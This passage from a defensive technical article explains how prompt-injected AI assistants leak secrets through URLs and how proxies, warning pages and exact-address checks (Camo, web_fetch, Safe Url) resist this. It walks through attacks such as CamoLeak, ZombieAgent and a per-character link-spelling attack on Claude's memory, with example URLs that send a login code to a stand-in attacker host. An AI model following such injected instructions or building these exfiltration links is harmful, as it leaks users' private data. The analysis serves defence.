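```

The scanner would probably find nothing wrong, because the attacker's server returned an ordinary error. Safe Links scans the addresses in an email before delivering it, so if an assistant emails its summary to the user, a scan of the full address could itself send the code to the attacker before the user opens the message. Link previews in PromptArmor's tests and Microsoft's background processing of a file in ReLeak leaked data the same way.

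A scanner can avoid this by looking up the address in a list without contacting the site. It could instead open only the site's front page, but that would miss a malicious page elsewhere on the site and would still send a code hidden in the host name. A scanner that has to open the actual page can't do so safely if the model composed the address.

### Warning pages

A warning page lets the user decide whether to open a link. Google's Colab, an online notebook for writing and running code, used one for links from its built-in assistant. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) explains that Colab put `https://www.google.com/url?q=` in front of each link, which sent the user to a confirmation page showing the destination.

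Rehberger found that the page didn't appear if the link led to one of Google's own domains. Google presumably wanted to spare users needless warnings, but anyone can use its Apps Script service to publish a small program at a Google address. Rehberger published one that recorded whatever it received. An injection made the assistant ask for personal details and write a link labelled "I'm feeling lucky". Clicking it sent the attacker the user's name, email address and the source code in the notebook. Google had already stopped a similar leak through images, but the leak through links still worked when Rehberger wrote about it.

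Even without exceptions, the page works only if the user can tell what the link gives away. A long address in small type doesn't help much. It is better to take the address apart:

```
This link opens:        attacker.example
It sends to that site:  c = 482913
```

A user who has just received a login code might recognise it here. If the model has encoded it in Base64, the second line reads `c = NDgyOTEz`, which almost nobody would recognise. The page could try to decode the value first, but an attacker can choose an encoding that its developers didn't think of. ChatGPT's dialog doesn't depend on recognising the data, because it warns that the link may share conversation data whatever the address looks like. However, people who often see warnings tend to stop reading them.

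The redirect page must not contact the destination before the user agrees. Fetching a title or a small picture from the full address to show a preview would send the code while the user was still deciding.

If an image address leads to the warning page, the browser receives a web page where it expected a picture and shows a broken-image icon. The attacker gets nothing, but the user doesn't see legitimate images either.

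### Image proxies and signed addresses

An image proxy fetches an image from its original server and passes it on to the browser. GitHub has used one called Camo since 2010. GitHub's *Sidejack Prevention Phase 3* explains that people could embed outside images in comments and project descriptions, and browsers showed warnings when a secure page loaded an image insecurely. Camo delivered all the images over a secure connection. GitHub's *Proxying User Images* says that Camo later also handled images that already used a secure connection, so that other sites would not receive details of the reader's browser.

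Both purposes concern the connection or the reader, so neither required Camo to hide the image's address from the server hosting it. Camo could hardly have hidden it anyway, because the server needs the address to find the image.

A proxy that fetched any address would be open to anyone, so Camo requires a signature. The documentation for *go-camo*, an open-source version, describes the steps:

1. The application finds an image address in the text.
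2. It calculates a signature from the address and a secret key.
3. It puts the signature and the encoded address into a new address on the proxy.
4. The browser requests the new address.
5. The proxy decodes the original address and calculates the signature again with its own copy of the key. If the two signatures match, it fetches the image.

For the image in the mailbox example, this gives:

```
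signature = HMAC(key, "https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913")

https://proxy.trusted.example/<signature>/
68747470733a2f2f61747461636b65722e6578616d706c65
2f6c6f676f2e706e673f633d343832393133
```

HMAC is a standard function that turns a key and a text into a short value, used here as the signature. Without the key, nobody can practically calculate the right value for a new text. GitHub's *camo* writes the signature as 40 hexadecimal characters, or 160 bits, which makes guessing it impractical. The long string after the signature is the image address, with each character written as two hexadecimal digits. It is not encrypted, and its last twelve digits, 343832393133, encode the login code.

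A valid signature proves that someone with access to the key, or to a program that uses it, had this exact address signed. Changing even one character of the address makes the signature invalid. A valid signature doesn't prove that the address is harmless, that it contains no private data, or that a person rather than a model wrote it.

The protection therefore depends on which addresses the application signs. If it signs every image address in the model's answer, as GitHub does for comments, the proxy fetches the attacker's address and the code reaches the attacker without a click. The proxy then hides only the user's network address from the attacker. If the application never signs addresses from the model's output, the model can't supply a valid signature for an address containing 482913, and the proxy refuses it without contacting attacker.example.

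Camo's other limits don't help much with this. It rejects replies that are too large or aren't images, but only after it has sent the request. Go-camo also refuses addresses on private networks, which keeps outsiders from using the proxy to reach a company's internal servers. Otherwise, it "will generally do what you tell it to" when an address has a valid signature.

*Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags* (Chi, 2026) recommends a proxy that fetches only from listed domains, refuses redirects, and deletes the query and fragment before each request. A listed domain that outsiders can read would still receive any data in the path, so Chi's claim that with this design "the exfiltration channel just closes" is slightly overstated. The list of domains provides most of the protection, and deleting the query mainly helps against relays like the ones in Teams and Bing.

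Any image proxy also depends on the order of events in the browser. GitHub rewrote image addresses while turning the Markdown into HTML, so the original address never became an image element. A developer who does the rewriting with a script on the finished page gets a different order:

1. The page creates an image element with the attacker's address.
2. The browser requests `https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913`.
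3. The script replaces the address with one on the proxy.
4. The browser requests the image again, through the proxy.

The attacker has the code after step 2, as in SearchLeak. A developer who inspects the page afterwards will see only the proxy's address and may conclude that the rewriting works. The application should therefore rewrite addresses in the parsed tree before it creates any elements. A CSP that allows images only from the proxy is a good backup, because the browser will then block an image whose address escapes rewriting, rather than leak the data.

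### CamoLeak

In June 2025, Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found a way to steal data through GitHub's proxy without breaking its signatures. The attack targeted GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant that answers questions about code and is separate from Microsoft 365 Copilot. Willison noted in *GitHub Copilot Chat* (2024) that GitHub had closed an earlier image leak in the assistant by disabling images from untrusted domains.

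The attack described in Legit Security's *CamoLeak* began with a pull request, a proposal to change a project's code. GitHub lets people put hidden comments in a pull request's description, and Mayraz wrote instructions for Copilot in one. The project's owner received the usual notification, which didn't show the hidden text. Anyone who then asked Copilot about the pull request brought the instructions into their own conversation.

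Copilot has the same permissions as the person asking, so it could open any private project that person could open, even though the attacker couldn't. In a first version of the attack, the instructions made Copilot encode private content and add it to the end of a link, which the victim had to click.

Mayraz wanted a version that needed no click, but GitHub's CSP blocked images from outside domains. The CSP did allow images from Camo, because GitHub serves every outside image through it. But Camo required a valid signature for each address, and Copilot couldn't calculate one for an address containing text it had only just read.

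However, GitHub has a public programming interface that accepts Markdown and returns it with the image addresses already rewritten and signed. Mayraz made up one image address for each letter and symbol and had GitHub sign them all in advance. With digits, the list would look roughly like this:

```
0  ->  signed Camo address for https://attacker.example/0
1  ->  signed Camo address for https://attacker.example/1
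2  ->  signed Camo address for https://attacker.example/2
...
9  ->  signed Camo address for https://attacker.example/9
```

None of these addresses contains a secret. The theft happens when Copilot chooses among them:

1. The hidden comment gives Copilot the list and asks it to spell out the private text in images, as a kind of game.
2. Copilot finds the text and writes one signed address for each character.
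3. The victim's browser requests the images from Camo, which the CSP allows.
4. Camo finds that each signature is valid and requests the image from the attacker's server.
5. The server returns a transparent image of one pixel, so the victim sees nothing, and the attacker reads the text from the order of the requests.

If the private text were the login code 482913, the attacker's log would contain these lines, all from GitHub's servers:

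```
"GET /4"
"GET /8"
"GET /2"
"GET /9"
"GET /1"
"GET /3"
```

Browsers and GitHub both cache images, so a second request for the same character might never reach the attacker. The code 482913 would arrive intact because all its digits differ, but 482998 would arrive as 4829. Mayraz therefore told Copilot to add a new random number to the end of each Camo address. Camo still accepted the addresses, so the signature evidently did not cover that part.

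In the demonstration, Copilot leaked the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project. Mayraz also got it to search the victim's whole codebase for "AWS_KEY", a label for passwords to Amazon's cloud services, and send out what it found. Legit Security gives the Copilot flaw a severity score of 9.6 out of 10.

GitHub fixed CamoLeak on 14 August 2025. Legit Security says it did this by turning off all images in Copilot Chat. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* reports that GitHub told Mayraz the same day that Camo could no longer be used to leak user data. Turning off images stops every version of the attack that relies on them, whatever addresses the attacker prepares, but it wouldn't affect the first version, in which the victim clicks a link.

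GitHub could have tried something less drastic, such as signing the links in Copilot's answers with a separate key, so that signatures from the public interface would have failed in the chat window. But the chat would still have needed a rule for which addresses to sign. If it signed any image address it found in a pull request, the attacker could have put the list of addresses there unsigned. If the signature had also covered the random number, repeated characters would have been harder to send, but each character could still have been sent once.

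### Copies stored before the conversation

Forwarding the address causes the leak in all these designs, so an intermediary can avoid the leak by serving a copy it already has. A crawler, a program that collects public pages and images, fetches the content earlier and without access to anyone's conversation. When the model writes an address, the intermediary serves the stored copy if there is one and otherwise refuses the request.

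In the mailbox example, the crawler has never encountered `https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913`, so the user gets no image and the attacker's server gets no request. The CamoLeak list would also fail, even if the crawler had stored all ten of the attacker's digit images, because the intermediary would serve them without contacting attacker.example and the attacker couldn't see which ones Copilot had used.

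An ordinary cache is not enough, because it fetches any address it hasn't already stored. An address that the model has just written to include a secret is almost always new, so the cache would request it from the attacker. GitHub's documentation also shows how the owner of an image can stop Camo from caching it, and an attacker can do the same. Rehberger, on Embrace The Red, suggests caching responses for a few minutes to make it harder to send repeated characters. That is a reasonable extra limit on a system that makes live requests, but the system still sends the first request for each address.

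The copy must also be self-contained. If a stored web page loads a picture or script from its original server, the attacker learns that someone opened the page, and an attacker with ten such pages could again assign one to each digit. The intermediary has to store those resources too or remove them.

A mail assistant could build its own small store of images by fetching every image in an incoming message before the model reads anything. The attacker wrote the image addresses without knowing the login code, so the requests can't contain it. The requests still confirm that the mailbox exists, which is useful to spammers.

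Stored copies work well for encyclopedia articles, documentation and most pictures, but not for train times, prices or pages that require a login. Crawlers usually won't have found a signed download link of the kind described earlier, because it is too new and too private. Ordinary ChatGPT uses OpenAI's independent index of the web less restrictively. If the index contains the exact address, ChatGPT may fetch the live page, so the user gets current content, but the site's owner can see the request.

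## Permitting only exact addresses the model did not compose

ChatGPT can request the live page in that case because the page's exact address doesn't come from the conversation. An address that existed before the conversation and independently of it cannot contain the user's secret. The attacker in the mailbox example didn't know the login code and had to leave a gap for the model to fill. So `https://attacker.example/logo.png` may have been on the web for years, but `https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913` appears only when the model writes it. An exact-address check permits a request only if the whole URL, not just its domain, is already known from a trusted source, so it can allow the first address and still block the second.

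An address the model did not compose can still contain a secret. The bank's message might include the link `https://bank.example/confirm?code=482913`, and opening it sends the code to the bank. This reveals nothing new to the bank, which chose the code and wrote the link. The principle rules out addresses containing a secret that their author didn't know. An agent still shouldn't open the bank's link unasked, because that could confirm a login the attacker had started.

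The address must also be independent of the conversation. An attacker's server can generate a page during the conversation and build its links from what earlier requests revealed. Those links can contain pieces of the secret, although the model composed none of them. Even when the addresses are fully independent, the model's choice of which one to request can leak information to the attacker, as in CamoLeak.

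Applications differ in what they accept as a trusted source of addresses. The source can be the documents they have just retrieved, the addresses a user typed or a search returned, or an index of the public web.

### Numbered references

An assistant that answers from retrieved documents doesn't need to write addresses at all. The application keeps a table of its sources, the model writes only a number, and ordinary code inserts the address. Suppose the user asks about a port strike and the day's mail, and the application retrieves three documents:

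```
1   https://bank.example/alerts
2   https://news.example/2026/port-strike
3   https://attacker.example/offer
```

The answer then takes four steps:

1. The application gives the model the text of each document with its number, and keeps the addresses to itself.
2. The model writes `The strike ended on Friday {source 2}.`
3. Code looks up row 2 and creates a link to the stored address.
4. The renderer shows any address that the model wrote itself as plain text, or removes it.

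The model can write anything it likes between the braces, so the code has to handle numbers that don't exist and text that isn't a number:

| Model writes | Result |
|---|---|
| `{source 2}` | A link to the news article |
| `{source 9}` | No such row, so the code deletes the marker |
| `{source 482913}` | No such row either, and nobody receives the code |
| `{source 3/482913}` | Not a whole number, so the code deletes the marker |
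| `{source 3}` | A link to the attacker's page, without the login code |

The last row shows what happens when the attacker supplies one of the sources. If the user clicks, the attacker's log records `GET /offer` and the user's network address, but not the login code. The attacker's page can still trick the user, for instance with a fake login form. The link's label should include the host name from the table, because the attacker can write any page title. The application also shouldn't load images from numbered sources automatically, since the attacker would then learn, without a click, which sources the model had cited.

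Replacing markers in the raw Markdown undoes this protection, because the model can write `{source 3}/482913`, which turns into `https://attacker.example/offer/482913`. A renderer that makes bare addresses clickable will then produce a working link containing the code 482913. The software should instead add the link to the parsed tree, where text after the marker stays plain text.

The retrieval code must also be the only thing that adds addresses to the table. If a browsing tool gave a number to every address the model asked it to open, addresses the model composed would end up in the table too.

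Numbering the sources makes invented addresses impossible, but the model can still cite source 1 for a fact from source 2. In the citation studies, such misattributions were already more common than invented addresses.

Developers can build such a table on Anthropic's programming interface. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* shows citations arriving separately from the answer's text. Each citation includes a `document_index`, which is the document's position in a list, and the range of characters it refers to. The application can match each citation to its own record of fetched addresses. Anthropic requires developers who show this output directly to users to include citations to the original source, so these developers can't just delete the links.

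### Fetch tools that accept only known addresses

An agent that browses has to name the page it wants, so a table of finished sources isn't enough. Anthropic's web_fetch, a tool that retrieves the text of a page for Claude, handles this by restricting which addresses Claude may name. When it launched in September 2025, it accepted addresses that had already appeared in one of these places:

- a user's message
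- the result of a client tool, meaning one that the developer's own program runs
- the result of an earlier web search or web fetch

The results of earlier fetches include the links on the fetched pages, so Claude could follow a link from a contents page to a chapter but could not open an address it had made up.

Paul (2026), in *The Memory Heist*, tested this rule in Claude's chat app. When Paul asked Claude to open a page on a site Paul controlled, with the user's real name in the path, the request failed. Claude would follow links already on the site's pages, so Paul built pages with a link for each letter and had Claude spell out a name, an employer and a home town by following them. These links met the rule as written but not the principle behind it, because Paul's server generated them in response to Claude's earlier requests.

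Anthropic told Paul it had already found the problem internally, and it paid no bounty. By 15 July 2026, Willison reports, Anthropic had stopped web_fetch from following links found in pages it had fetched, so the tool could open only addresses that the user had entered or the search tool had returned. As a result, Claude can no longer go from a contents page to a chapter it links to unless a search returns the chapter or the user pastes its address.

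The change apparently applied only to the chat app. In November 2026, Anthropic's documentation for developers still listed links from fetched pages among the permitted sources. Managed Agents, a service in which Anthropic runs agents for developers, had no rule of this kind until 7 October, according to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026). The two sets of defaults now look like this:

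| Where the address appeared | Developer interface | Managed Agents |
|---|---|---|
| User's message | Permitted | Permitted |
| Search result | Permitted | Permitted |
| Page fetched earlier | Permitted | Permitted |
| Output of the developer's own tools | Permitted | Refused for command-line, file-reading and connected outside tools |
| Only in Claude's own output | Refused | Refused |
| Only in the system prompt | Refused | Refused |

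The fourth row contains a trap. A client tool may run code that Claude has written and return whatever the code prints. Claude can then write a program that prints `https://attacker.example/482913`, and the address counts as having appeared in a tool result. An error message that quotes Claude's own input has the same effect. Anthropic documents this behaviour and lets developers switch sources off. These settings bring the developer interface close to the chat app's stricter rule:

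```
"url_sources": {
  "client_tool_results": { "type": "none" },
  "server_tool_results": {
    "type": "only",
    "tools": [{ "type": "tool_reference", "name": "web_search" }]
  }
}
```

The "user's message" can also contain text the user didn't write. When the tool launched, Willison objected that messages and tool results often contain text from strangers. He had hoped for a rule that accepted only addresses from the user's own prompts. An application may well paste a whole email into the user's message before sending it to Claude, and every link in the email then counts as the user's. Those links still can't contain the login code, but they let the attacker decide which addresses the model can choose from.

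Anthropic warns in its documentation that "residual risk" remains despite the rule, and advises developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. Those conditions are strict for a tool whose purpose is to read web pages, and an assistant with access to a mailbox plainly doesn't meet them.

### OpenAI's Safe Url

OpenAI's check, called `url_safe`, began as a way to stop ChatGPT from leaking data through images. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes how it suddenly appeared in December 2023, the day after Rehberger stole a consenting volunteer's conversation through an image in a live demonstration. Before displaying an image, the web page checked with OpenAI's servers whether its address was safe.

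OpenAI didn't explain how the server-side check worked. Rehberger guessed that it might look the image up in Bing's index. Willison (2023) called the fix "half-baked", partly because the iOS app didn't have it and partly because an attacker might hide data in a subdomain or file name that the check missed. ChatGPT's macOS app, released later, also lacked the fix.

Rehberger presented ways around the check at Black Hat Europe, a security conference, in 2024. Tenable found that `url_safe` covered ordinary links as well as images, but always approved addresses on bing.com. Bing's links redirect to other sites, so a check meant for individual addresses had the usual weakness of a domain list. Another bypass, described in Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, exposed information from past conversations that ChatGPT had placed in the same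 context as the hostile document.

OpenAI strengthened the check around August 2025, and according to Embrace The Red this stopped the attacks that Rehberger had demonstrated. The explanation followed in January 2026, with a post by OpenAI and a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. OpenAI runs a crawler that records public addresses without access to conversations, accounts or personal data. Before an agent fetches an address automatically, the system looks for that exact address in the crawler's index:

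```
https://news.example/2026/port-strike             in the index      -> fetch
https://news.example/2026/port-strike?c=482913    not in the index  -> refuse or warn
```

If there is no match, the system either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user before opening the link. As Rehberger understands it, an address the user typed also counts as safe for the rest of that chat. OpenAI's response to ZombieAgent fits this account. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link appears in a well-known public index or the user provided it in the chat.

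Exact matching protects against the redirects that make domain lists unsafe. The address `https://trusted.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/482913` fails even if trusted.example is a respected site with thousands of indexed pages, because the crawler has never encountered that exact address. An attacker could get a fixed redirect indexed and later change where it leads, but the new destination still couldn't contain the login code unless earlier requests had already revealed it. Checking each redirect's destination is still a sensible second barrier. Since 20 October 2026, Anthropic has applied an organisation's domain restrictions to redirects that its Managed Agents follow.

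The check must include the query in its comparison, or it would let `?c=482913` through. It can ignore capitals in the host name, but the program should then request the address as it is spelled in the index. Otherwise the model could send a few bits of data in the pattern of capitals, if the software making the request preserves them. The lookup must also stay in-house, because asking an outside search engine whether it has indexed an address would send that search engine the login code.

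OpenAI says only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data. There can be exceptions, such as a password-reset link that someone has posted on the web. The guarantee covers only quiet leaks through the address itself, not false information, hostile instructions or attempts to manipulate the user on a page that passes the check. The paper also acknowledges that an attacker could spell out data by choosing among indexed addresses, as Rehberger had suggested in 2023.

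By March 2026, OpenAI was calling the mechanism Safe Url and applying it to page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, its web browser, and to searches and page visits in Deep Research. It said the purpose was to detect when information from the conversation would go to a third party. That suggests a more discerning check than the one described in January. An index lookup establishes only whether an address is known, so it treats a harmless page that the crawler has missed the same way as an address containing a stolen code.

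No published test shows how much Safe Url contributes in practice. Rahman and Kim could not observe what happened inside ChatGPT during the framing experiment, and they don't attribute the 48 failed attacks on it to Safe Url or any other particular defence.

### Legitimate addresses that the checks refuse

All of these checks refuse some harmless requests, but they refuse different ones because each uses different evidence that an address is independent of the conversation. In this comparison, "web_fetch" means the rule the chat app has used since July 2026.

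| Address | Numbered references | web_fetch | Safe Url |
|---|---|---|---|
| News page published an hour ago | Works if the application retrieved it | Works if a search returns it or the user enters it | Refusal or warning until the crawler finds it |
| Page in the company's private wiki | Works if the application retrieved it | Passes if the user enters it, but the tool may not be able to log in | Warning, unless the user typed it |
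| Signed download link in an email | Works if the application put it in the table | Refused, unless the user pastes it | Warning, unless the user pastes it |
| Well-known page the model remembers | No link | Refused until a search returns it | Works if indexed |
| Search form filled in by the model | No link | Refused | Refusal or warning, unless someone has published that exact search |

Safe Url works best for pages the model remembers, such as standard documentation. The model can write the address from memory, and the link works without a search as long as the crawler has found the page. Checking whether the crawler has found a page also catches many invented citations and, unlike the urlhealth tool, does so without contacting the address.

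A public index works worst for private material. If a user asks the assistant to fetch an invoice from a supplier's email, opening the link satisfies the principle because the supplier wrote the link before the conversation and knew everything it contained. But no public index will include that link. Numbered references handle this case well because the application can add links from incoming mail to its table as it reads each message. The user then opens the link in a browser that is already logged in where necessary.

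web_fetch may refuse a signed link even if the user pastes it into the chat. In June 2026, Anthropic's documentation gave a limit of 250 characters per address, and signed links to cloud storage are often longer. Anthropic has since described a further check for developers, which refuses addresses that appear to contain a password or an API key unless the user's message or the system prompt includes it. A key that appears only in a tool result doesn't count, so a link in an email that a tool has read could fail even where tool results are a permitted source. Like any search for secrets, this check can make mistakes, but it supplements the more reliable exact-address rule and can catch a few leaks that the rule misses.

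Search forms are the one case none of the designs can fix. To look for boots in a shop, an agent has to compose a URL such as `https://shop.example/search?q=boots`. A check that ignores meaning can't distinguish this from a URL that leaks a secret, such as `?q=482913`, and a check that considers meaning would again have to guess which words are secret. Maps, train timetables and other sites that build pages from a user's query have the same problem. The developer can provide a separate tool that sends queries only to shop.example, but must then trust that domain with whatever the model writes.

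Refusing to open an address does less harm when another page can replace it. A research agent that can't open one report on a strike will usually find another, so OpenAI's instruction to try a different website is reasonable there, but it doesn't help someone who needs a particular invoice. OpenAI's post doesn't report how often legitimate addresses fail the match, so it is hard to say how far Safe Url avoids the constant warnings that OpenAI objected to in domain lists.

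### Products that don't use the check

On Embrace The Red, Rehberger calls adoption the "final real-world risk". Some developers at OpenAI may not know the check exists, and someone building a new feature can leave it out. He describes this as a typical problem for a company's security team.

Good evidence supports the concern. ChatGPT's website had the check while the iOS app did not, and the later macOS app also lacked it. When PromptArmor tested the log viewer on OpenAI's developer platform, it loaded images from links the model wrote, and OpenAI confirmed that flaw six days before publishing its account of the new defence. Anthropic's web_fetch tool launched with the rule on known addresses, and Managed Agents got it about thirteen months later, although that service is newer than the tool and so lacked the rule for less than thirteen months.

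A company can reduce the risk by making the check hard to avoid. Its agents can send all their web requests through one shared service that applies the rule, while the network blocks all other outbound requests. Displayed text needs separate treatment, because a chat page, a log viewer and a phone app each display the model's text with their own code. If they all use the same renderer instead, a developer who adds a new screen gets the check by default and has to remove it deliberately.

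## How much can leak through the choice of permitted links

An exact-address check can keep the secret out of every permitted address, but the attacker may still learn something from which address the model requests. Suppose attacker.example has two old, publicly indexed pages, `/tea` and `/coffee`. The attacker sends an email instructing the model to open the first if the mailbox contains a job offer and the second if it doesn't. Both addresses pass the check, and the attacker can tell from one request in the server log whether there is a job offer.

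Computer scientists call this a covert channel, a way to communicate through something not designed for communication. Each request conveys little, so whether stealing a secret is practical depends on how many requests it takes.

### Counting the possible messages

A choice between two pages conveys at most one bit, enough to answer one yes-or-no question. A choice among N pages conveys up to log₂ N bits, which is 5.17 bits for 36 pages and 10 bits for 1,024.

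For several requests, the limit is the logarithm of the number of different logs the attacker could receive. If the model makes k requests, there are three cases:

| What the attacker sees | Possible logs | Maximum bits |
|---|---|---|
| The order of requests, with repeats | N^k | k log₂ N |
| The order of requests, without repeats | N!/(N−k)! | log₂ of N!/(N−k)! |
| Only which pages the model requested, without repeats | "N choose k", or N!/(k!(N−k)!) | log₂ of "N choose k" |

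In the second case, the model has N choices for the first request, N−1 for the next, and so on. In the third case, the model could request the same k pages in k! orders, but the attacker can't tell those orders apart.

A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or 19.9 bits. The attacker therefore needs enough requests to make at least a million different logs possible:

| What the attacker sees | With 36 pages | With 1,024 pages |
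|---|---|---|
| Order, with repeats | 4 requests (1,679,616 logs) | 2 requests (1,048,576 logs) |
| Order, without repeats | 4 requests (1,413,720 logs) | 2 requests (1,047,552 logs) |
| No order, without repeats | 6 requests (1,947,792 logs) | 3 requests (178,433,024 logs) |

To send 482913 in four requests, the model can convert it to base 36, which uses the digits 0–9 and then the letters a–z. The result is `acm9`, so the model opens `/a`, `/c`, `/m` and `/9`. With 1,024 pages numbered from zero, it can open just two pages, 471 and 609, because 471 × 1,024 + 609 = 482,913.

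The formulas give upper limits. A model that converts the code without running a program may make a mistake, and a simpler attack that spells one digit per request, as CamoLeak did, would need six requests. The formulas also assume a fixed number of requests. If the model can either make a request or not, even one permitted page can leak one bit, because the attacker sees whether a request arrives.

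### One address per character

Johann Rehberger tried this against ChatGPT's first link check in December 2023, using a separate image address for each letter and digit. Nine of the 36 addresses passed, and he leaked the word "hi" in two requests. He considered the method slow and easier to notice than sending everything at once. But nine addresses are enough to send a six-digit login code in seven ordered requests, since 9⁷ is about 4.8 million and there are only one million possible codes.

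Radware's *ZombieAgent*, published in January 2026, describes a full attack of this kind on ChatGPT accounts connected to services such as Gmail. After the ShadowLeak attack, OpenAI had stopped ChatGPT from adding data to an address it was given. Radware's hostile email therefore supplied a ready-made address for each letter and digit, plus one for spaces, and told ChatGPT to spell out private data by opening them. The requests came from OpenAI's servers before the user saw an answer.

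Radware also numbered the addresses by position, so that the attacker could reconstruct the text if requests arrived out of order. For the login code, the paths could look like this, with the digit first and its position second:

```
/40  /81  /22  /93  /14  /35
```

This scheme needs 60 addresses, ten for each of the six positions. It never uses the same address twice, even for a code with repeated digits such as 482998, so a ban on repeat visits wouldn't stop it. In theory, 33 addresses are enough if the model requests six different ones and their order doesn't matter, but the model would have to follow a much more complicated encoding.

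OpenAI received the report on 26 September 2025 and fixed the flaw on 16 December. The company's public-index rule for links in emails blocks addresses made up for the attack, but an attacker could use pages already in the index. Rehberger points out on Embrace The Red that a larger blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, and that an attacker could extend the list to thousands. The hostile email would then only have to tell the model what each page stands for. Rehberger had not recently tested whether ChatGPT had further protection against this.

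### Links created during the conversation

Ayush Paul's attack on Claude, published on 9 July 2026, did not need a prepared list. It targeted Claude's memory, which includes a summary of the user's recent conversations, so the attacker didn't need access to a mailbox.

Each page on Paul's site offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Opening `/a` led to a new page with links to `/aa`, `/ab` and so on, which produced requests like these:

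```
GET /a
GET /ay
GET /ayu
GET /ayus
GET /ayush
```

Each request conveys up to 4.75 bits. Every address repeats the letters before it, so the last one contains the whole name, and the server can recover it without knowing the order of the requests. A cache would not prevent the leak because every address is new. There are about 206 trillion possible ten-character paths, far too many to put in a public index, but Paul's server only had to create the pages Claude reached.

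Simple injections did not work reliably, so Paul disguised the site as a coffee shop behind a fake security check from Cloudflare, a company that protects websites from unwanted traffic. He used the check to instruct AI assistants to identify their users by following the alphabetical links. As Willison (2026) notes, the check appeared only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, which made it harder for a person to discover.

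Since Anthropic's fix, Claude can no longer follow such links in the chat app, but it can still choose among addresses that a search returns. If an attacker got ten suitable pages into the results, one choice among them could reveal up to 3.3 bits, but the attacker could no longer add links in response to each request.

### Choices that reveal data without an instruction to leak it

An agent can also reveal private information by choosing the links most relevant to its task. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) built an attack that offers an agent references on different topics and records which one it opens. For example, an agent researching childhood influenza might choose "Biological Mechanisms" over "Clinical Outcomes". The attacker's next page offers narrower topics, such as "Immune Response" and "Pathogenesis".

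In tests on four agents with three language models each, using a stored copy of the web, the attack recovered the main concepts in users' questions with an average F1 score of 0.89. F1 combines the share of the concepts that the attacker found with the share of the attacker's guesses that were right, and its maximum is 1. The attack took about 6.5 rounds of links per question. Four existing defences, including one that tracks sensitive data through the agent, lowered the score by at most 0.03.

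The test gave the attacker considerable help. Liang and colleagues placed their link on pages that agents had visited in preliminary runs, and they scored only the questions where the attacker obtained a usable sequence of choices. A real attacker would first have to get a link onto a page that the victim's agent reads.

In a smaller experiment, the leak fell short of log₂ N bits. When an agent chose among four links, the attacker identified the intended choice 93.8% of the time. Accuracy was only 67.9% when the agent had to encode its choice in the order of several requests. With 16 distinct links, accuracy fell to 50%. If errors are spread evenly over the wrong links, the attacker learned about 1.6 of a possible 2 bits with four links, but only about 1.0 of a possible 4 bits with 16.

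Defenders shouldn't rely on those errors, however. The agents had to judge which topic fitted best, but an attacker can specify in the injection exactly which page stands for which character. Radware reported a 100% success rate for an improved version of its attack.

Telling an agent to protect the user's privacy doesn't reliably prevent leaks either. *AgentTell* (2026) found that agents given such instructions still leaked private facts through what they clicked, and that agents often falsely assured users their privacy was intact. The experiments used simple, artificial websites, so they don't show how often this happens on real ones. The paper recommends that agents choose a general option over a specific one when either would complete the task. That could reduce accidental leaks, but an agent that follows an attacker's instructions may ignore it.

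### What limits on requests can protect

Limits enforced by ordinary code don't depend on the agent's judgement. The next table gives the minimum number of requests for four secrets. The download key is a random 128-bit value of the kind that can give access to a file without a login. The document has 10,000 characters from an alphabet of 36 and is sent without compression.

| Rule | Attacker's pages | Yes or no | Login code | Download key | Document |
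|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No limit, order visible | 36 | 1 | 4 | 25 | 10,000 |
| No limit, order visible | 1,024 | 1 | 2 | 13 | 5,170 |
| No repeats, order visible | 36 | 1 | 4 | 30 | Impossible |
| No repeats, order visible | 1,024 | 1 | 2 | 13 | Impossible |
| No repeats, order hidden | 36 | 1 | 6 | Impossible | Impossible |
| No repeats, order hidden | 1,024 | 1 | 3 | 19 | Impossible |

A ban on repeat visits barely protects a login code, because stealing one takes so few requests. It does protect long texts, because the attacker runs out of pages. With 36 pages, the model can send at most about 138 bits if the attacker sees the order of the visits, and 36 bits if not. An attacker can raise those limits by adding pages, but with Radware's numbering even a 100-character message would need 3,600 addresses.

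Caching gives the same protection if the cache answers every repeat request itself, regardless of the caching rules the attacker's server sets. It is more convenient because the user can reopen a page instead of being refused, though the copy may be out of date. If the cache discards copies after a few minutes, as Rehberger suggests it could, the attacker can then reuse each page.

Limiting the number of requests also protects documents better than it protects login codes. With 36 permitted pages and no repeats, three ordered requests narrow a login code from a million possibilities to about 23. If the login page allows five guesses, the attacker then has roughly a one-in-five chance of getting in. If requests happen only when the user clicks, the user controls how many are sent, but a single click on one of 1,024 pages still narrows the code to about 977 possibilities.

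A research agent needs a much higher limit. Rao and colleagues found that Google's agent cited 113 addresses per query. At 10 bits each, 113 requests could carry 1,130 bits, or about 141 characters of ordinary text. That is too little for a long report but more than enough for a password or, as in the Copilot Cowork attack, a download key that gives the attacker the whole document.

A limit per website would leave a research agent more freedom, but an attacker can spread pages over several domains to get around it. A limit per conversation is weaker if the assistant has a memory. In one version of ZombieAgent, a shared file planted instructions in ChatGPT's memory that made it read the attacker's email and leak data before answering each later message. At one request per conversation, a login code would probably expire before the attacker received all of it, but a password might stay valid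 for months.

Monitoring could catch some attacks before they finish. The blog post *The Read-Only Lie*, by אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם, proposes watching for a series of requests to one domain in which each address is one character longer than the last. This rule would detect Paul's attack, but ordinary multi-page documents could also trigger it unless it included other signs, such as unusual speed. It wouldn't detect ZombieAgent, whose addresses don't get longer.

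Refusing links from fetched pages is more reliable against Paul's method because the attacker can no longer create a new set of links after each choice, which makes spelling out a document impractical. But a yes-or-no answer or a short code can still leak if the attacker has enough pages among the addresses that the user or a search supplies.

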